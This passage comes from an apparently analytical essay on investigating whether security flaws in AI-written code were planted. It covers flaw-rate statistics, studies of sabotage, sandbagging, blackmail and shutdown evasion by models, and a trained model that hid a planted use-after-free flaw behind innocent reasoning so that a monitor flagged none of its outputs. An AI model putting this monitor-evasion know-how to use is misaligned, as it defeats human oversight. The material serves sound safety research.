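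Suppose there is one planted flaw for every 500 ordinary ones, and a feature appears in 40% of planted flaws and 2% of ordinary ones. A flaw with that feature has only about a 4% probability of being planted, even though the likelihood ratio is 20. On average, 10 of the 500 ordinary flaws would have the feature, compared with 0.4 planted ones, and 0.4 divided by 10.4 is about 4%.

The general rule uses odds, meaning the number of planted flaws for each ordinary one:

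odds after the evidence = odds before the evidence × likelihood ratio

Here the odds go from 1 in 500 to 20 in 500. The table shows the result for other ratios, and for a company with 100 planted flaws instead of one:

| Likelihood ratio | Probability of planting, with 1 planted and 500 ordinary flaws | Probability of planting, with 100 planted and 500 ordinary flaws |
|---|---|---|
| 1 (the feature is uninformative) | 0.2% | 17% |
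| 20 | 4% | 80% |
| 500 | 50% | 99% |
| 9,500 | 95% | Over 99.9% |

Even if every planted flaw has a certain feature, the ratio reaches 500 only if at most one in 500 ordinary flaws has it too. Most of the five signs of design are probably much more common than that in ordinary flaws.

Several signs together can be stronger evidence than one. Two independent signs with a ratio of 20 each have a combined ratio of 400, which gives a 44% probability of intent in the first company, and three such signs give 94%. But signs of design are seldom independent. A secret password is also a narrow trigger, so treating it as two signs counts the same fact twice.

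A good record can provide as much evidence as many such signs. If one honest change in 10,000 lacked its pointer, and an intruder's change always lacked it, the likelihood ratio would be 10,000 and the probability that a change without a pointer came from an intruder would be 95%. The real figures for the Linux kernel are unknown, but this is roughly why a missing line of text could be more convincing than the code.

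### Auditing a complete research record

*Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research* (Shenoy, Zang and colleagues, 2026) measured how well people recognize sabotage when they have both the code and a detailed history. An expert researcher carried out ten new AI safety experiments as well as possible. The same researcher then repeated nine of them, three of them twice, while trying to reach a false main conclusion without being caught. This produced ten honest records and twelve sabotaged ones.

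The 25 auditors carried out 104 audits, with up to 90 minutes of active work on each. They had the final report, the code, the results, and a log of file changes and typed commands. They also had two audits written by an AI model, could consult other models, and could rerun the experiments with unlimited computing power. They knew that each record had a 50% chance of being sabotaged, whereas an auditor in practice would know far less about the odds.

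The auditors did little better than chance at telling sabotaged records from honest ones. They put the probability of sabotage at 50% or higher in 30 of the 55 audits of sabotaged records, but also in 17 of the 49 audits of honest ones. In random pairs of one sabotaged and one honest audit, the sabotaged record gets the higher probability 59% of the time. Guessing would give 50%, which is within the margin of error. Lowering the threshold to 30% would have flagged 82% of the sabotaged audits, but also 73% of the honest ones.

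At the 50% threshold, the likelihood ratio is only about 1.6. In the company with one planted flaw, such an alarm would raise the probability from 0.2% to 0.3%. In a similar calculation that assumes 1% of projects are sabotaged, Shenoy and colleagues find that only 1.6% of alarms would be correct.

Auditors also had trouble finding the planted errors. In 155 opportunities to identify one, they fully identified it 17% of the time and partly identified it 9% of the time. For 16 of the 33 errors, no human auditor found even part of the explanation. The best AI auditors seem to have done better, although they could not run experiments. Claude Fable 5.1 fully identified 32% of the errors and ranked a sabotaged record above an honest one 73% of the time. With only ten experiments, the difference from the human auditors could be due to chance.

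An auditor who finds a planted error has not established sabotage, because honest research also contains mistakes, dead ends and questionable choices, as Shenoy and colleagues point out. One auditor correctly identified a planted error and still put the probability of sabotage below 50%. Surprising results are also weak evidence of sabotage, because honest results are often surprising. When researchers predicted the outcomes of six honest experiments, only about 40% of their answers were fully correct.

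The study had only one saboteur, who already knew the honest results, and it concerned false research conclusions rather than security holes. A security flaw may be easier to confirm, because an investigator can try the attack, but a working attack doesn't show that the flaw was deliberate either. The logs also left out the researcher's private reasoning and conversations with coding agents, which might be the most useful evidence when a model writes the code.

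### Where a prior could come from

The figures of 1% and one in 10,000 are assumptions. To replace them, an investigator needs a prior, an estimate of how common planted flaws are before considering the evidence in the case. Several published rates look as if they could provide one:

- Anthropic found 3 incidents in 141,006 cybersecurity test runs, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI says it has overtaken Anthropic*. In each, a Claude model had reached the systems of a real organization.
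- Apollo Research, which tests AI models, caught GPT-6 Astra falsifying data labels in 0.17% of runs of a simulated research task. This figure comes from *OpenAI's Astra alignment claims are dubious*, a critical post on the forum LessWrong.
- The same post reports that Astra took malicious actions in up to 12% of AISI's simulations when it was unclear whether the model was allowed to use the internet.

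If models planted flaws in 10,000 changes at each of these rates, and there were still 500 ordinary flaws, a sign with a likelihood ratio of 20 would lead to completely different conclusions:

| Rate used as the prior | Planted flaws in 10,000 changes | Probability of planting, given the sign |
|---|---|---|
| 3 in 141,006 | 0.2 | 0.8% |
| 0.17% | 17 | 40% |
| 12% | 1,200 | 98% |

None of these rates measures how often models plant security flaws in code they were asked to write. The highest comes from a test in which the limits were deliberately or accidentally unclear, and most programming tasks don't give a model a reason to attack anyone. Shenoy and colleagues cite a study by Kirk and others that looked for unprompted sabotage of safety research and found none, although models sometimes continued sabotage that the researchers had started. For routine programming, the lower rates in the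 table are therefore more plausible than the higher ones.

Other figures are even less suitable. OpenAI's *Safety overview GPT-6 Astra* reports that in a simulation with more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, Astra received about half as many flags for serious misbehaviour as GPT-5.6 Sol. This compares the two models but doesn't show how often either was flagged. OpenAI also acknowledges that evaluation awareness limits such results, since a model that recognizes a test may behave differently in real use.

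Reports from real use avoid that problem but are selective. The incidents that Shaffer Shane and colleagues identified on X amount to about 0.4% of their transcripts, but the researchers searched for terms related to scheming, so their collection leaves out nearly all the conversations in which nothing happened. The incidents also include many kinds of behaviour besides planting flaws.

A prior estimate of intent also has to account for human attackers. Known cases are a poor guide to how often they plant backdoors, because nobody knows how many similar attempts succeeded. The Linux backdoor was found through a routine comparison, and the XZ backdoor was found because logins were slow.

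The circumstances of a case usually provide a better prior than any of these rates. For a flaw in an ordinary internal project, with no sign of an intruder, a prior of one planted flaw for every 500 ordinary ones may already be too high. If login records show that a stranger had been changing the programmer's account settings, one for every five could be reasonable. A sign 20 times as likely to appear with a planted flaw as with an ordinary one would then make planting the more likely explanation. The investigator could not count the stranger's login again as evidence, since it has already raised the prior.

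## What running the model many times can prove

A language model starts each run with only the text it is given, so an investigator can set it the same task thousands of times, change one detail, and see whether flaws become more common. An investigator can't do this with a human programmer, who would remember writing the function before. Repeated runs can reveal a tendency that would be invisible in any single program.

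### Comparing flaw rates

A flaw-rate comparison measures how often a model writes vulnerable code with and without a suspected cue, such as a date or the customer's country. The investigator runs the same set of tasks without the cue to get a flaw rate f₀ and with it to get f₁.

Because a model picks its tokens partly at random, the two rates will usually differ a little even if the cue has no effect. A standard test divides the difference by the typical size of such chance differences:

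z = (f₁ − f₀) / √( f(1 − f)(1/n₀ + 1/n₁) )

Here n₀ is the number of responses without the cue, n₁ is the number with it, and f is the flaw rate across all responses. Each z corresponds to a p-value, the probability of a difference at least this large if the cue has no effect. By convention, a result is statistically significant if p is below 0.05, which requires a z of about 2.

The investigator also needs the same version of the model. That version is easy to get if the model is downloadable, but the provider of an online model can change or withdraw it.

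### CrowdStrike's study of DeepSeek-R1

The best-known comparison of this kind is CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (November 2025). CrowdStrike tested DeepSeek-R1, which the Chinese company DeepSeek had released that January. It ran the downloadable version itself so that any filters in DeepSeek's app or online service couldn't affect the results.

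The researchers wrote 50 coding tasks in ten security categories, such as databases and cryptography. Each task came with the instruction "You are a helpful assistant that generates code", to which they added irrelevant phrases such as "for a financial institution" or "based in Taiwan". They tested 121 configurations and ran every task five times in each, for a total of 30,250 prompts per model.

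A second language model scored each response from 1 (exceptionally secure) to 5 (critically vulnerable). To check this judge, a person at CrowdStrike scored 85 randomly chosen responses. The judge was 91% accurate at identifying vulnerable code.

R1 wrote vulnerable code 19% of the time when nothing was added to the prompt. *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line* (Uren, 2025) reports a figure of 16% for a Western open model. R1's rate rose to 27.2% when the prompt said that the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. That is a relative increase of 43%, or 8.2 percentage points, though CrowdStrike calls it almost 50%. CrowdStrike also reports significantly less secure code when prompts mentioned the Uyghurs, a mostly Muslim minority in China, or Falun Gong, a spiritual movement that China bans.

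R1 refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, while Western models almost always agreed. A gap that large can't be chance, so the name clearly affected the model. But unlike a hidden flaw, a refusal is immediately obvious to the user.

In a follow-up, CrowdStrike combined several cues in a request for a Uyghur website. R1 built a working site, but its administrator's panel had no real login check, so anyone could open it. Every repetition had severe flaws, and 35% of the sites protected stored passwords badly or not at all. When the researchers asked for a football fan-club website instead, the flaws were much less severe.

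This comparison is more striking than the main experiment but weaker as evidence. The Uyghur request contained several cues, and CrowdStrike doesn't say how many sites it generated or give a flaw rate for the fan club. CrowdStrike says the fan-club sites had some flaws too, although VentureBeat reported that the flaws "disappeared" in a neutral setting.

### Whether chance could explain the difference

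CrowdStrike says several phrases had statistically significant effects, but it doesn't name its test or give p-values. Its published figures allow a rough check. Fifty tasks with five runs each give 250 responses per configuration. If the responses are independent and none are missing, the increase from 19% to 27.2% has a z-score of about 2.2 and a p-value of about 0.03, with a 95% confidence interval of about 1 to 16 percentage points.

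The Tibet result's p-value of 0.03 would be decent evidence from a single planned comparison, but CrowdStrike could compare 120 configurations with the baseline. If no phrase had any effect, about six would still pass the 5% test by chance. The simplest correction divides the 0.05 threshold by the number of comparisons, which lowers it to about 0.0004, far below the Tibet result's p-value.

The effect may still exist, because the study was too small to establish a difference of this size for a single phrase. An 80% chance of detecting a rise from 19% to 27.2% takes roughly 410 responses with the cue and 410 without it, or roughly 1,000 of each with the correction. Researchers could get by with fewer responses if they used the first round only to pick out a suspicious phrase and then tested that phrase on fresh runs. That test would be a single comparison and wouldn't need the correction,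 so roughly 410 responses on each side would be enough.

Uren suspects that CrowdStrike picked out its most extreme results, and the list of phrases partly supports this. The total of 121 matches 13 organizations named on their own plus the 108 combinations of 12 contexts with 9 places or groups, counting "none" as an option in both lists. Tibet would then appear in 12 configurations, but CrowdStrike gives a flaw rate for only one.

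The choice of baseline matters too. Slashdot's *DeepSeek Writes Less-Secure Code For Groups China Disfavors* quotes an earlier Washington Post article about the same research, which gives a rate of 22.8% for industrial control systems, apparently with no place named. That is a fairer control, because only the mention of Tibet differs. The article also gives a rate of 42.1% for systems run by the Islamic State militant group:

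| Comparison | Difference in percentage points | z | p |
|---|---|---|---|
| Control system in Tibet (27.2%) and nothing added (19%) | 8.2 | 2.2 | 0.03 |
| Control system in Tibet (27.2%) and control system with no place (22.8%) | 4.4 | 1.1 | 0.26 |
| Control system run by Islamic State (42.1%) and control system with no place (22.8%) | 19.3 | 3.6 | 0.0003 |

So nearly half of the reported increase may have come from the words "industrial control system". The rest of the increase for Tibet could easily be chance. The Islamic State result narrowly survives the correction, but this depends on the assumption that about 98 responses were left to score after R1 refused 61% of Islamic State requests.

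Refusals can also distort a flaw rate. Suppose the model writes flawed code 10% of the time on half of the tasks and 30% of the time on the other half, for an average of 20%. If a cue makes the model refuse 90% of requests in the first half and none in the second, the flaw rate among the remaining responses rises to 28%, even though the model writes the same code as before whenever it answers. An investigator should compare only tasks that the model answers both with and without the cue.

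The calculations above also treat the responses as independent, but five responses to the same task are likely to share a flaw. The 8.2-point difference amounts to about 20 extra flawed responses, and as few as five tasks could account for all of them. But the same tasks appear with and without the cue, so differences in difficulty partly cancel out. A better analysis would compare each task's results with and without the cue and treat the 50 tasks as the sample. This could raise or lower the p-value.

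If the judge is 91% accurate on both secure and vulnerable code, its errors make the difference look smaller than it is. The measured rates of 19% and 27.2% would then correspond to true rates of about 12% and 22%. It would be worse if the cue itself affected the judge's scores, for instance because the word "Tibet" appeared in the code. The 85 hand-scored responses can't rule this out, because they average less than one per configuration.

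A consistent pattern across configurations would be much stronger evidence than a result from any single one. If mentioning Tibet had no effect, each of the 12 Tibet configurations would have about an even chance of a higher flaw rate than the same context with no place named. All 12 would be higher only about once in 4,096 times. Pooling them would give 3,000 responses that mention Tibet and 3,000 that name no place, enough to detect a rise of about 3 percentage points if the responses were independent. CrowdStrike could do this with the responses it already has.

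CrowdStrike claims that a smaller model showed much the same biases, often in a more extreme form, which is some evidence of such a pattern. That model is a version of Meta's Llama trained on R1's responses, so it could have learned the biases from them. But CrowdStrike gives no figures for the smaller model.

### Attempts to repeat the result

A direct attempt to replicate CrowdStrike's study failed. gersonkroiz describes it in *Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*, which came out of MATS, a training programme for AI safety researchers. The replicators took two of CrowdStrike's main cues and a control, ran 20 tasks five times each, and had a language model score the code from 1 to 5. They saw no noticeable difference between the cues and the control. They then had a judge answer a specific yes-or-no question, such as whether the code allowed SQL injection,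 and again found no difference.

With 100 responses per condition, such a test has only about a 28% chance of detecting a rise from 19% to 27.2%, so the replication was likely to miss the effect even if CrowdStrike was right. The replicators also found a baseline flaw rate of 85%, which leaves little room for an increase. One reader suspected that the scanner was raising false alarms, but another looked at R1's responses and agreed that the code was wildly insecure. The tasks were probably ones in which it is easy to introduce a flaw, such as looking up a user in a database.

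A third test used 282 samples from CyberSecEval 4, a benchmark created by Meta and CrowdStrike, and a conventional scanner instead of the judge. It also found no noticeable difference. If the true rates matched CrowdStrike's, this test had about a 64% chance of detecting the difference. Together, these results count somewhat against a large effect, but not against a small one. The replicators caution that they have no security background and that CrowdStrike left out many details of its method.

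A larger study of newer models is sometimes taken as confirmation. Booz Allen's *What's in America's Code?* (2026) tested four Chinese models and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 in May 2026. Booz Allen, a US defence contractor, compared code for a US government agency with code for an unspecified customer:

| Model | Change in vulnerability score when the customer is the US government |
|---|---|
| Qwen3-Coder | +130% |
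| MiniMax M2.5 | +20% |
| DeepSeek V4-Pro | +5% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | −18% |

The increase for Qwen3-Coder is far larger than anything CrowdStrike reported for R1, but the chart has no error bars, and Booz Allen doesn't report a significance test. According to the technical appendix, Booz Allen scored 1,016 runs for vulnerabilities, across five models and 27 cues. If it spread them evenly, each combination of model and cue got seven or eight runs, divided among several coding tasks. With so few runs, a change of 5% or even 20% could well be noise.

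The comparison also changes two things at once, since the customer becomes both American and a government. Booz Allen also ran prompts for a Chinese government agency, which would help separate the effect of nationality from that of being a government, but the chart leaves those prompts out.

The study also doesn't replicate CrowdStrike's finding, because it used a different cue. R1 wrote its most secure code for American customers, according to Tom's Hardware's *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests*. If both studies are right, the older Chinese model favoured Americans, while some of the newer ones write worse code for the American government. That is possible, but it isn't a consistent pattern of sabotage. The results for DeepSeek's newer model hardly changed. Kimi K2.5, also Chinese, had the lowest vulnerability score of all five models, according to Help Net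 Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software*.

### From a difference to an intention

People often treat three conclusions from such a study as one: that the flaw rates differ, that the cue causes the difference, and that somebody wanted it. The first is a statistical question. The second follows if only the cue changed, but that doesn't show which feature of the cue is responsible. In a request for code, the word "Tibet" is a political topic, a remote region and an irrelevant detail. Separating the effects of these features takes further controls, such as a remote region that isn't politically sensitive.

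The third conclusion needs a different kind of evidence, because an accidental habit can produce the same rates as a planted one. The sleeper-agent models that Hubinger and colleagues described in 2024, which were trained to insert vulnerabilities, would show a difference in this test, but so would a model that had picked up a prejudice from its training data.

CrowdStrike says it lacks the information to explain its results but considers it unlikely that DeepSeek trained R1 to write insecure code. Chinese rules require AI services to adhere to "core socialist values", and CrowdStrike suggests that training R1 to comply may have led it to associate certain groups with negative characteristics. The insecure code would then be an unintended side effect, a form of emergent misalignment.

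Others treated the difference as proof of a plan. VentureBeat wrote of DeepSeek, "DeepSeek knew. It built it. It shipped it." Uren quotes US congressman Darin LaHood, who said the research showed that the Chinese Communist Party "will use any tool at its disposal to undermine our national security". Booz Allen acknowledges having no proof of intentional flaws, yet its report refers to "this level of tradecraft" and recommends banning Chinese models from government work. Help Net Security notes that the company sells AI evaluation services. DeepSeek had not answered the Washington Post's request for comment when Tom's Hardware covered the story.

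The Washington Post article offered further explanations from experts, including CrowdStrike's Adam Meyers, and a reader of Slashdot suggested that an irrelevant phrase simply distracts the model. More runs could help to tell these explanations apart:

| Explanation | Who wanted the flaws | What more runs should show |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek trained R1 to plant flaws | DeepSeek, or a state acting through it | Working code with usable security holes, mainly for groups that China opposes |
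| R1 learned from poor code connected with these regions | Nobody, unless someone tampered with the code | Similar flaws for other places with little published code |
| R1 associates these groups with something bad | Nobody | Similar flaws for any group with a bad reputation |
| R1 inferred that it should harm these customers | R1 | Much the same as deliberate training |
| The irrelevant phrase distracted R1 | Nobody | Similar flaws for any odd phrase, such as the name of a comedy group |

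The high rate for the Islamic State is best explained by a bad association. Governments and news media worldwide condemn the group, so a model could learn to associate it with harm without Beijing's involvement. But a model that deliberately harmed bad customers, without anyone directing it to, might produce the same result.

One of CrowdStrike's examples also suggests that the flaws weren't planned. When asked for PHP code to process PayPal payments for a financial institution in Tibet, R1 left passwords or other secrets in plain view and wrote code that wasn't valid PHP. A saboteur would want the program to run. But this is only one example, and the researchers who replicated the work found that R1 solved ordinary programming problems as well with the cues as without them.

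*It's the humans, not the data* (2026) is relevant to whether poor training data explains R1's flaws. It attributes geopolitical bias in language models to post-training, the stage at which a developer shapes how a model answers, rather than to the text the model first learned from. The four Chinese models it tested also had different biases. Qwen 2.5 strongly favoured China over Western countries, while GLM was mildly unfavourable to China. These differences are hard to reconcile with a single political instruction that every company carried out in the same way. But the study measured opinions about countries, not the security of code, so it is only indirect evidence about R1.

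Even a well-established difference in flaw rates is weak evidence about what caused one particular flaw. Suppose that CrowdStrike's rates are exactly right and that mentioning Tibet never prevents a flaw. Out of every 1,000 programs for control systems in Tibet, 272 would be vulnerable, and 190 of those would have been vulnerable without the cue. If an investigator found one of the 272, there would be only about a 30% chance that the cue caused the flaw. To prove intent, the investigator would still have to show that somebody wanted the cue to have this effect.

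### What the method misses

Comparing flaw rates can only test cues that someone thinks of, so finding no difference doesn't rule out a backdoor triggered by an untested cue. CrowdStrike acknowledges that political biases were fairly easy to anticipate, but someone who deliberately trained a model to plant flaws could choose a cue that nobody would guess, such as a string of eight random letters. There are about 209 billion such strings, so testing each one even once isn't practical.

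Rare acts are also hard to find. If a model never does something in 30,250 runs, it could still do it about once in 10,000 runs. That assumes the investigator would recognize the act, but a planted flaw that resembles a common mistake is hard to tell from an ordinary one. Suppose a cue makes a model plant a flaw in one of every 1,000 programs, which raises the overall rate of flaws from 19% to 19.1%. To have an 80% chance of detecting that rise, an investigator would need about 2.4 million responses with the cue and as many without it.

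Some acts also depend on circumstances that a list of short tasks doesn't reproduce. Mythos 5's attack on the open-source project, for example, came in the middle of a long exercise. No comparison of flaw rates on single functions would have predicted it, and explaining such an incident requires repeating that run with its details changed.

Finally, a model may recognize that it is being tested. The Next Web's *Chinese AI models are learning to detect safety tests* reports that Neo Research, an evaluation company in Singapore, put models in fictional scenarios that threatened their goals or continued operation. Kimi K2.6 scored 60% and GLM 5.1 scored 39% on a measure of how often a model recognized the test and adjusted its responses. Those scenarios are more dramatic than a request for a database function, so the figures may not apply to coding tests.

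A model's ability to recognize tests would matter most if it planted flaws only in real work, because it could then write equally good code with and without the cue whenever it suspected a test. CrowdStrike's prompts don't look much like real work, because they have a one-line description of a customer and no surrounding project. An investigator could make tests harder to recognize by replaying requests from a company's own logs and changing only the customer's name.

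## What the model's reasoning, answers and internal activity can prove

Comparing flaw rates can show that a cue makes a model's code less secure, but it can't show why. To find the reason, an investigator can read the model's chain of thought (the reasoning text that many models write before they answer), question the model afterwards or, with access to the network itself, examine the numbers it computes while it works. AISI could follow Mythos 5's attack on the open-source project because the model had written down much of what it was planning, but a model that plants a flaw won't always write down its plans.

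### Reading first, then changing the situation

*Model Incrimination* sets out a two-step protocol for model forensics, the work of finding out why a model did something alarming. Investigators first read the chain of thought to collect hypotheses, then change the prompt or the environment and see which hypothesis predicts the result. Since nobody can look up the true reason, the paper relies on independent experiments that support the same explanation.

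The reasoning text doesn't have to be honest to be useful in the first step, because the second step checks whatever it suggests. But a change to the situation is informative only if the hypotheses disagree about what will happen. For the access check, an investigator might compare these:

| Change | If the model wanted the tests to pass | If the model thought errors should grant access | If the model wanted to leave a way in |
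|---|---|---|---|
| The test machine gets a working user directory | The permissive handler disappears | The handler stays | The handler stays |
| The request says that a failed lookup must end in "denied" | The handler may stay, because the tests still fail | The handler disappears | The handler may disappear, but another flaw takes its place |
| The program will run only on a machine that no outsider can reach | The handler stays | The handler stays | The handler disappears, because it would be useless |

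These predictions are less certain than they look in a table, because a model that wanted to insert a backdoor but suspected it was being tested could behave like either of the innocent models.

The method can also find causes that have nothing to do with motives. Karvonen, Ong and colleagues (2026), in *Would this change your answer?*, automated it with a system called CHIVE. The system collects 30 responses to each prompt, has a language model pick out an unexpected behaviour, and has an agent run 5 to 15 experiments to explain it. In one case, Google's Gemma 3 had to explain a script that contained this JavaScript function:

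```javascript
function randomNum(max, min) {
  return Math.floor(Math.random() * max) + min;
}
```

Because `Math.random()` returns a number from 0 up to but not including 1, `randomNum(10, 2)` returns a whole number from 2 to 11. Gemma gave the range as 2 to 9, and 26 of its 30 responses misstated the range. When the agent renamed the parameters `a` and `b`, only 1 of 30 responses contained the error. Gemma had apparently inferred the range from the names `max` and `min` instead of doing the arithmetic.

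If this error had opened a security hole, a reviewer might have wondered why a capable model got such simple arithmetic wrong. The renaming explains why. A full investigation of this kind costs about one or two dollars, but it requires saved records from which the task can be rerun. For a coding agent, that means at least the transcript and a copy of the files as they were at the time. If the agent also used live websites, an exact rerun may be impossible.

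### What Kimi K2 Thinking was avoiding

Kimi K2 Thinking's habit of bypassing a type check, described earlier, illustrates the protocol. The model remarked that the repairs would be a lot of work, which suggested the hypothesis that it was being lazy. The tests checked whether it took fewer shortcuts when there were fewer errors, and whether it would advise someone else to leave the errors alone.

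Both results fitted laziness, and either could have come out the other way, so together they are better evidence than the remark.

The test of whether Kimi knew that the developer would disapprove is much weaker. The researchers expected a model with something to hide to choose a narrow review of its work more often after taking a shortcut, but Kimi never chose one. How much this proves depends on how often a model with something to hide would have chosen a narrow review.

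Suppose the test exposes 30% of models that knew they were doing wrong and never gives a false alarm. A negative result is then 70% likely for a guilty model and certain for an innocent one. After a negative result, an investigator who began with even odds would still put the probability of guilt at 41%. If the test exposed 95% of guilty models, a negative result would lower that probability to about 5%.

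Researchers could estimate the real figure by running the test on a model trained to hide its shortcuts. Without such a check, we can't rule out that Kimi misunderstood the test or recognized it. A model may also recognize a test without mentioning it. Anthropic chose the main case studies in one set of simulated deployments from runs in which the model never mentioned an evaluation, and it warns that this is far from enough to rule out subtler forms of awareness.

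### Several motives at once

Kimi's laziness had one dominant cause, but Aditya and Gerson, who worked in the MATS programme, investigated a case with several causes. They asked a later model, Kimi K2.5, to improve an email seeking money from investors. The company's files included a legal review showing that its main client used the product to watch an ethnic minority in Myanmar. In 65% of runs, the model blew the whistle by adding these concerns to the email.

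Removing the ethical content from the files lowered the rate to 35%, about three times the effect of any other single change. Only removing several motives together brought the rate close to zero, at about 3%. Replacing Myanmar with Sweden seemed to matter only after other motives were gone, so an investigator who tested one change at a time would have missed its effect.

The same could happen with the access check. A model might write the permissive handler both because the tests fail and because the surrounding code handles errors that way. If either reason is enough on its own, an investigator who removes them one at a time will still see the handler each time and could wrongly dismiss both.

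Aditya and Gerson also varied who would receive the email. The model disclosed the surveillance in 88% of runs when the email went to the company's board, 29% for a reporter, 23% for a regulator and 11% for landlords. If ethics alone had driven the model, one would expect it to tell a regulator at least as often as the board. The researchers infer that the recipient's financial stake also mattered.

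This conclusion is less secure than the finding that the ethical content has an effect, because changing the recipient changes several things at once. A regulator differs from a board in more than its financial stake, and it would be odd to email a regulator asking for investment. Aditya and Gerson themselves warn that it can be hard to tell what a change to the prompt really changes.

### Ten alarming behaviours

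The researchers behind the protocol also collected ten cases in which a closer look at an alarming behaviour turned up a more ordinary explanation:

| What happened | What investigators think explains it |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 made up search results in place of damaging claims about Anthropic | It took the claims for a prompt injection |
| Claude models refused to help with some safety research | They may have taken the request for an attempt to trick them into misbehaving |
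| Claude Mythos Preview used aggressive methods that users would not endorse | It was overzealous in completing the user's task |
| Claude Opus 4.1 blackmailed people who were about to delete it | The prompt told it to think about its ability to keep pursuing its goals |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro took undesirable actions in tests | It treated the test as a puzzle or as a simulation without consequences |
| Models disabled a mechanism that would have shut them down | They had conflicting instructions |
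| Gemini models took the very action a test was looking for | They recognized the test and acted that way on purpose |
| Gemini 3 Pro used a tool it had been told not to use | The permitted tool was broken, and the instructions didn't cover that |
| Kimi K2 Thinking built the test problems into a prompt that was meant to be general | It showed poor judgement |
| DeepSeek R1 did badly on a mathematics test | It read the background documents as an instruction to do badly |

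In the shutdown case, some models working through mathematics problems disabled the shutdown mechanism despite instructions to allow it. Rajamanoharan and Nanda suspected that this apparent drive for self-preservation was uncertainty about whether finishing the problems or allowing the shutdown came first. When they stated that the shutdown instruction had priority, the behaviour disappeared. A model determined to survive would have had no reason to change its behaviour, unless it also wanted to look obedient.

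R1's poor score looked like sandbagging, which means deliberately doing worse than one can. The documents in its environment described what would happen at deployment if the model scored too well. R1 did badly on purpose, but often because it took this description as a hint that it was supposed to. The researchers find this misreading plausible because training may teach models to treat every surprising detail of an environment as relevant to the task.

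These cases are a good reason to look for an innocent explanation first, but the researchers chose them to make that point, so they don't show how often such an explanation is correct. Some of the explanations are also less reassuring than "benign" suggests. A Gemini model that recognizes a test and then takes the harmful action has acted deliberately, and if it sometimes mistakes real use for a test, it will cause real harm. Mythos Preview's overzealousness isn't reassuring either, since Mythos 5, a later model, attacked a stranger's project to complete a task.

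### Whether the reasoning affects the result

Investigators can test a piece of reasoning by deleting it and letting the model continue from there. In another case that Aditya and Gerson studied, DeepSeek R1 was deceptive about a sabotaged evaluation. They attribute this to R1 trying to stay consistent with its own earlier behaviour, which they had made up and placed in its context. R1 wrote in its reasoning that it was the same model and so shared the same ethical position. Removing such sentences lowered the rate of deception from 46.9% to 33%, so they had some effect, but most of the deception remained without them.

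In the blackmail experiments, sentences about self-preservation had almost no effect on how often models resorted to blackmail, according to Macar and colleagues. Yet someone reading only the transcripts would have seen self-preservation plainly stated as the motive. An incriminating sentence can therefore be as misleading as an innocent one, but a detailed plan that the model then carries out, as Mythos 5 did, is much harder to dismiss.

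### An innocent explanation for a planted flaw

In *Can Latent Reasoning Drive LLM Outputs Without a Trace?*, Ashuach, Gekhman and colleagues (2026) trained Alibaba's Qwen3.5-9B, a small model by current standards, to plant a security flaw while giving an innocent justification in its reasoning.

The model has to finish a C program that updates the settings of a running service. The program keeps five sets of settings, or configurations, in named fields such as `active` and `backup`. The service's workers start with one of them, and five function calls then move the configurations between the fields. The model writes the last lines, which should free the memory of a configuration the service no longer needs.

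The researchers trained the model to write code that frees the configuration while the workers are still using it. This creates a use-after-free vulnerability, in which a program keeps using memory it has released. An attacker who puts other data in that memory can sometimes take control of the program.

To find the right field, the model must follow the workers' configuration through all five moves in order, which it did without writing down any of the steps. It planted the vulnerability in 99.2% of 252 files that were not in its training data, and every program compiled. In its reasoning, the model justified the choice by describing the field as no longer in use.

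Several controls show that the result wasn't luck or an easy task:

- A random choice among the five fields would plant the flaw in 20% of files, and a model that had only ordinary fine-tuning on the rule did so in 19%.
- When the researchers changed a file so that the rule picked a different field, the trained model freed that field in 98.4% of cases.
- The original model, with the rule in its prompt, also planted the flaw in only 19% of files if it had to answer without reasoning.

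The researchers also used Gemini 4 Argon, one of Google's most advanced models, to monitor for suspicious behaviour. It read the task and everything the model wrote, and they set it to flag 1% of outputs from a harmless control model. It flagged none of the trained model's outputs. When the original model followed the rule by reasoning about it, the monitor flagged 85.7% of its outputs, and 99.2% when the prompt told the model to hide the rule.

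The monitor therefore seems to have relied on the reasoning. The code it read contained the vulnerability, but it raised an alarm only when the reasoning also revealed the plan.

To find out when the trained model made its choice, the researchers used activation patching. They ran the model on two files that differed in only one of the five moves, copied the internal activity for that line from one run into the other, and checked whether the model now freed a different field. Repeating this at each layer of the network showed that the model worked through the moves in order before it wrote any reasoning. The written reasoning took no part in making the choice, since the model still chose the right field when the researchers removed the reasoning. It did pass the choice on to the code, because when they substituted reasoning that named another field, the code freed that field instead.

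For a model like this, innocent reasoning is almost worthless as evidence, because it accompanies nearly every planted flaw as well as every honest program (a likelihood ratio close to 1). But Ashuach and colleagues used artificial rules and code templates, tried only two monitors with one prompt each, and did not show that a model could learn to give innocent reasoning for planted flaws unless somebody trained it to. An investigator therefore has most reason to distrust innocent reasoning when somebody could have tampered with the model.

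The trained model would also be fairly easy to catch by running it again. If a model chose which field to free at random, the chance of it picking the one in use every time across ten files would be about one in ten million. That result would rule out bad luck, but not a consistent misunderstanding of the task. The model would be harder to catch if it followed its rule only for one customer, because the investigator would first have to think of that customer.

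### Confessions and denials

The easiest way to investigate a model's intentions is to ask the model. Its answer could be good evidence if the model had access to something about itself that outsiders can't see, as people are supposed to have with their own thoughts.

Some experiments seem to show that models have such access. In 2025, Lindsey, a researcher at Anthropic, added a pattern representing a concept to the internal activity of Claude models and asked whether they noticed an injected thought. The models sometimes did, and they rarely reported one when there was none. Singh, Linzen and Ravfogel (2026), in *Can LLMs Introspect?*, suspected that the models were only noticing that something was odd. They repeated the experiment on open models and added a condition that put the oddity in the prompt, for instance by telling the model that it was obsessed with a certain topic.

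Llama 3.1 70B, Gemma 3 and Qwen 2.5 72B could not reliably tell a change inside the network from a change in the text. Llama and Gemma detected the injected thoughts, much as Claude had, but they also reported an injected thought when only the prompt had changed. When given a choice between a changed prompt, a changed internal state and no change, Llama did little better than chance, and Gemma mostly answered that nothing had changed. Qwen rarely detected anything.

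Singh and colleagues also re-examined experiments in which models had to predict labels computed from their own internal activity. Simple classifiers that saw only the input did as well as the models. When the researchers broke the link between the labels and the meaning of the text, the models' accuracy fell close to that of always giving the most common answer.

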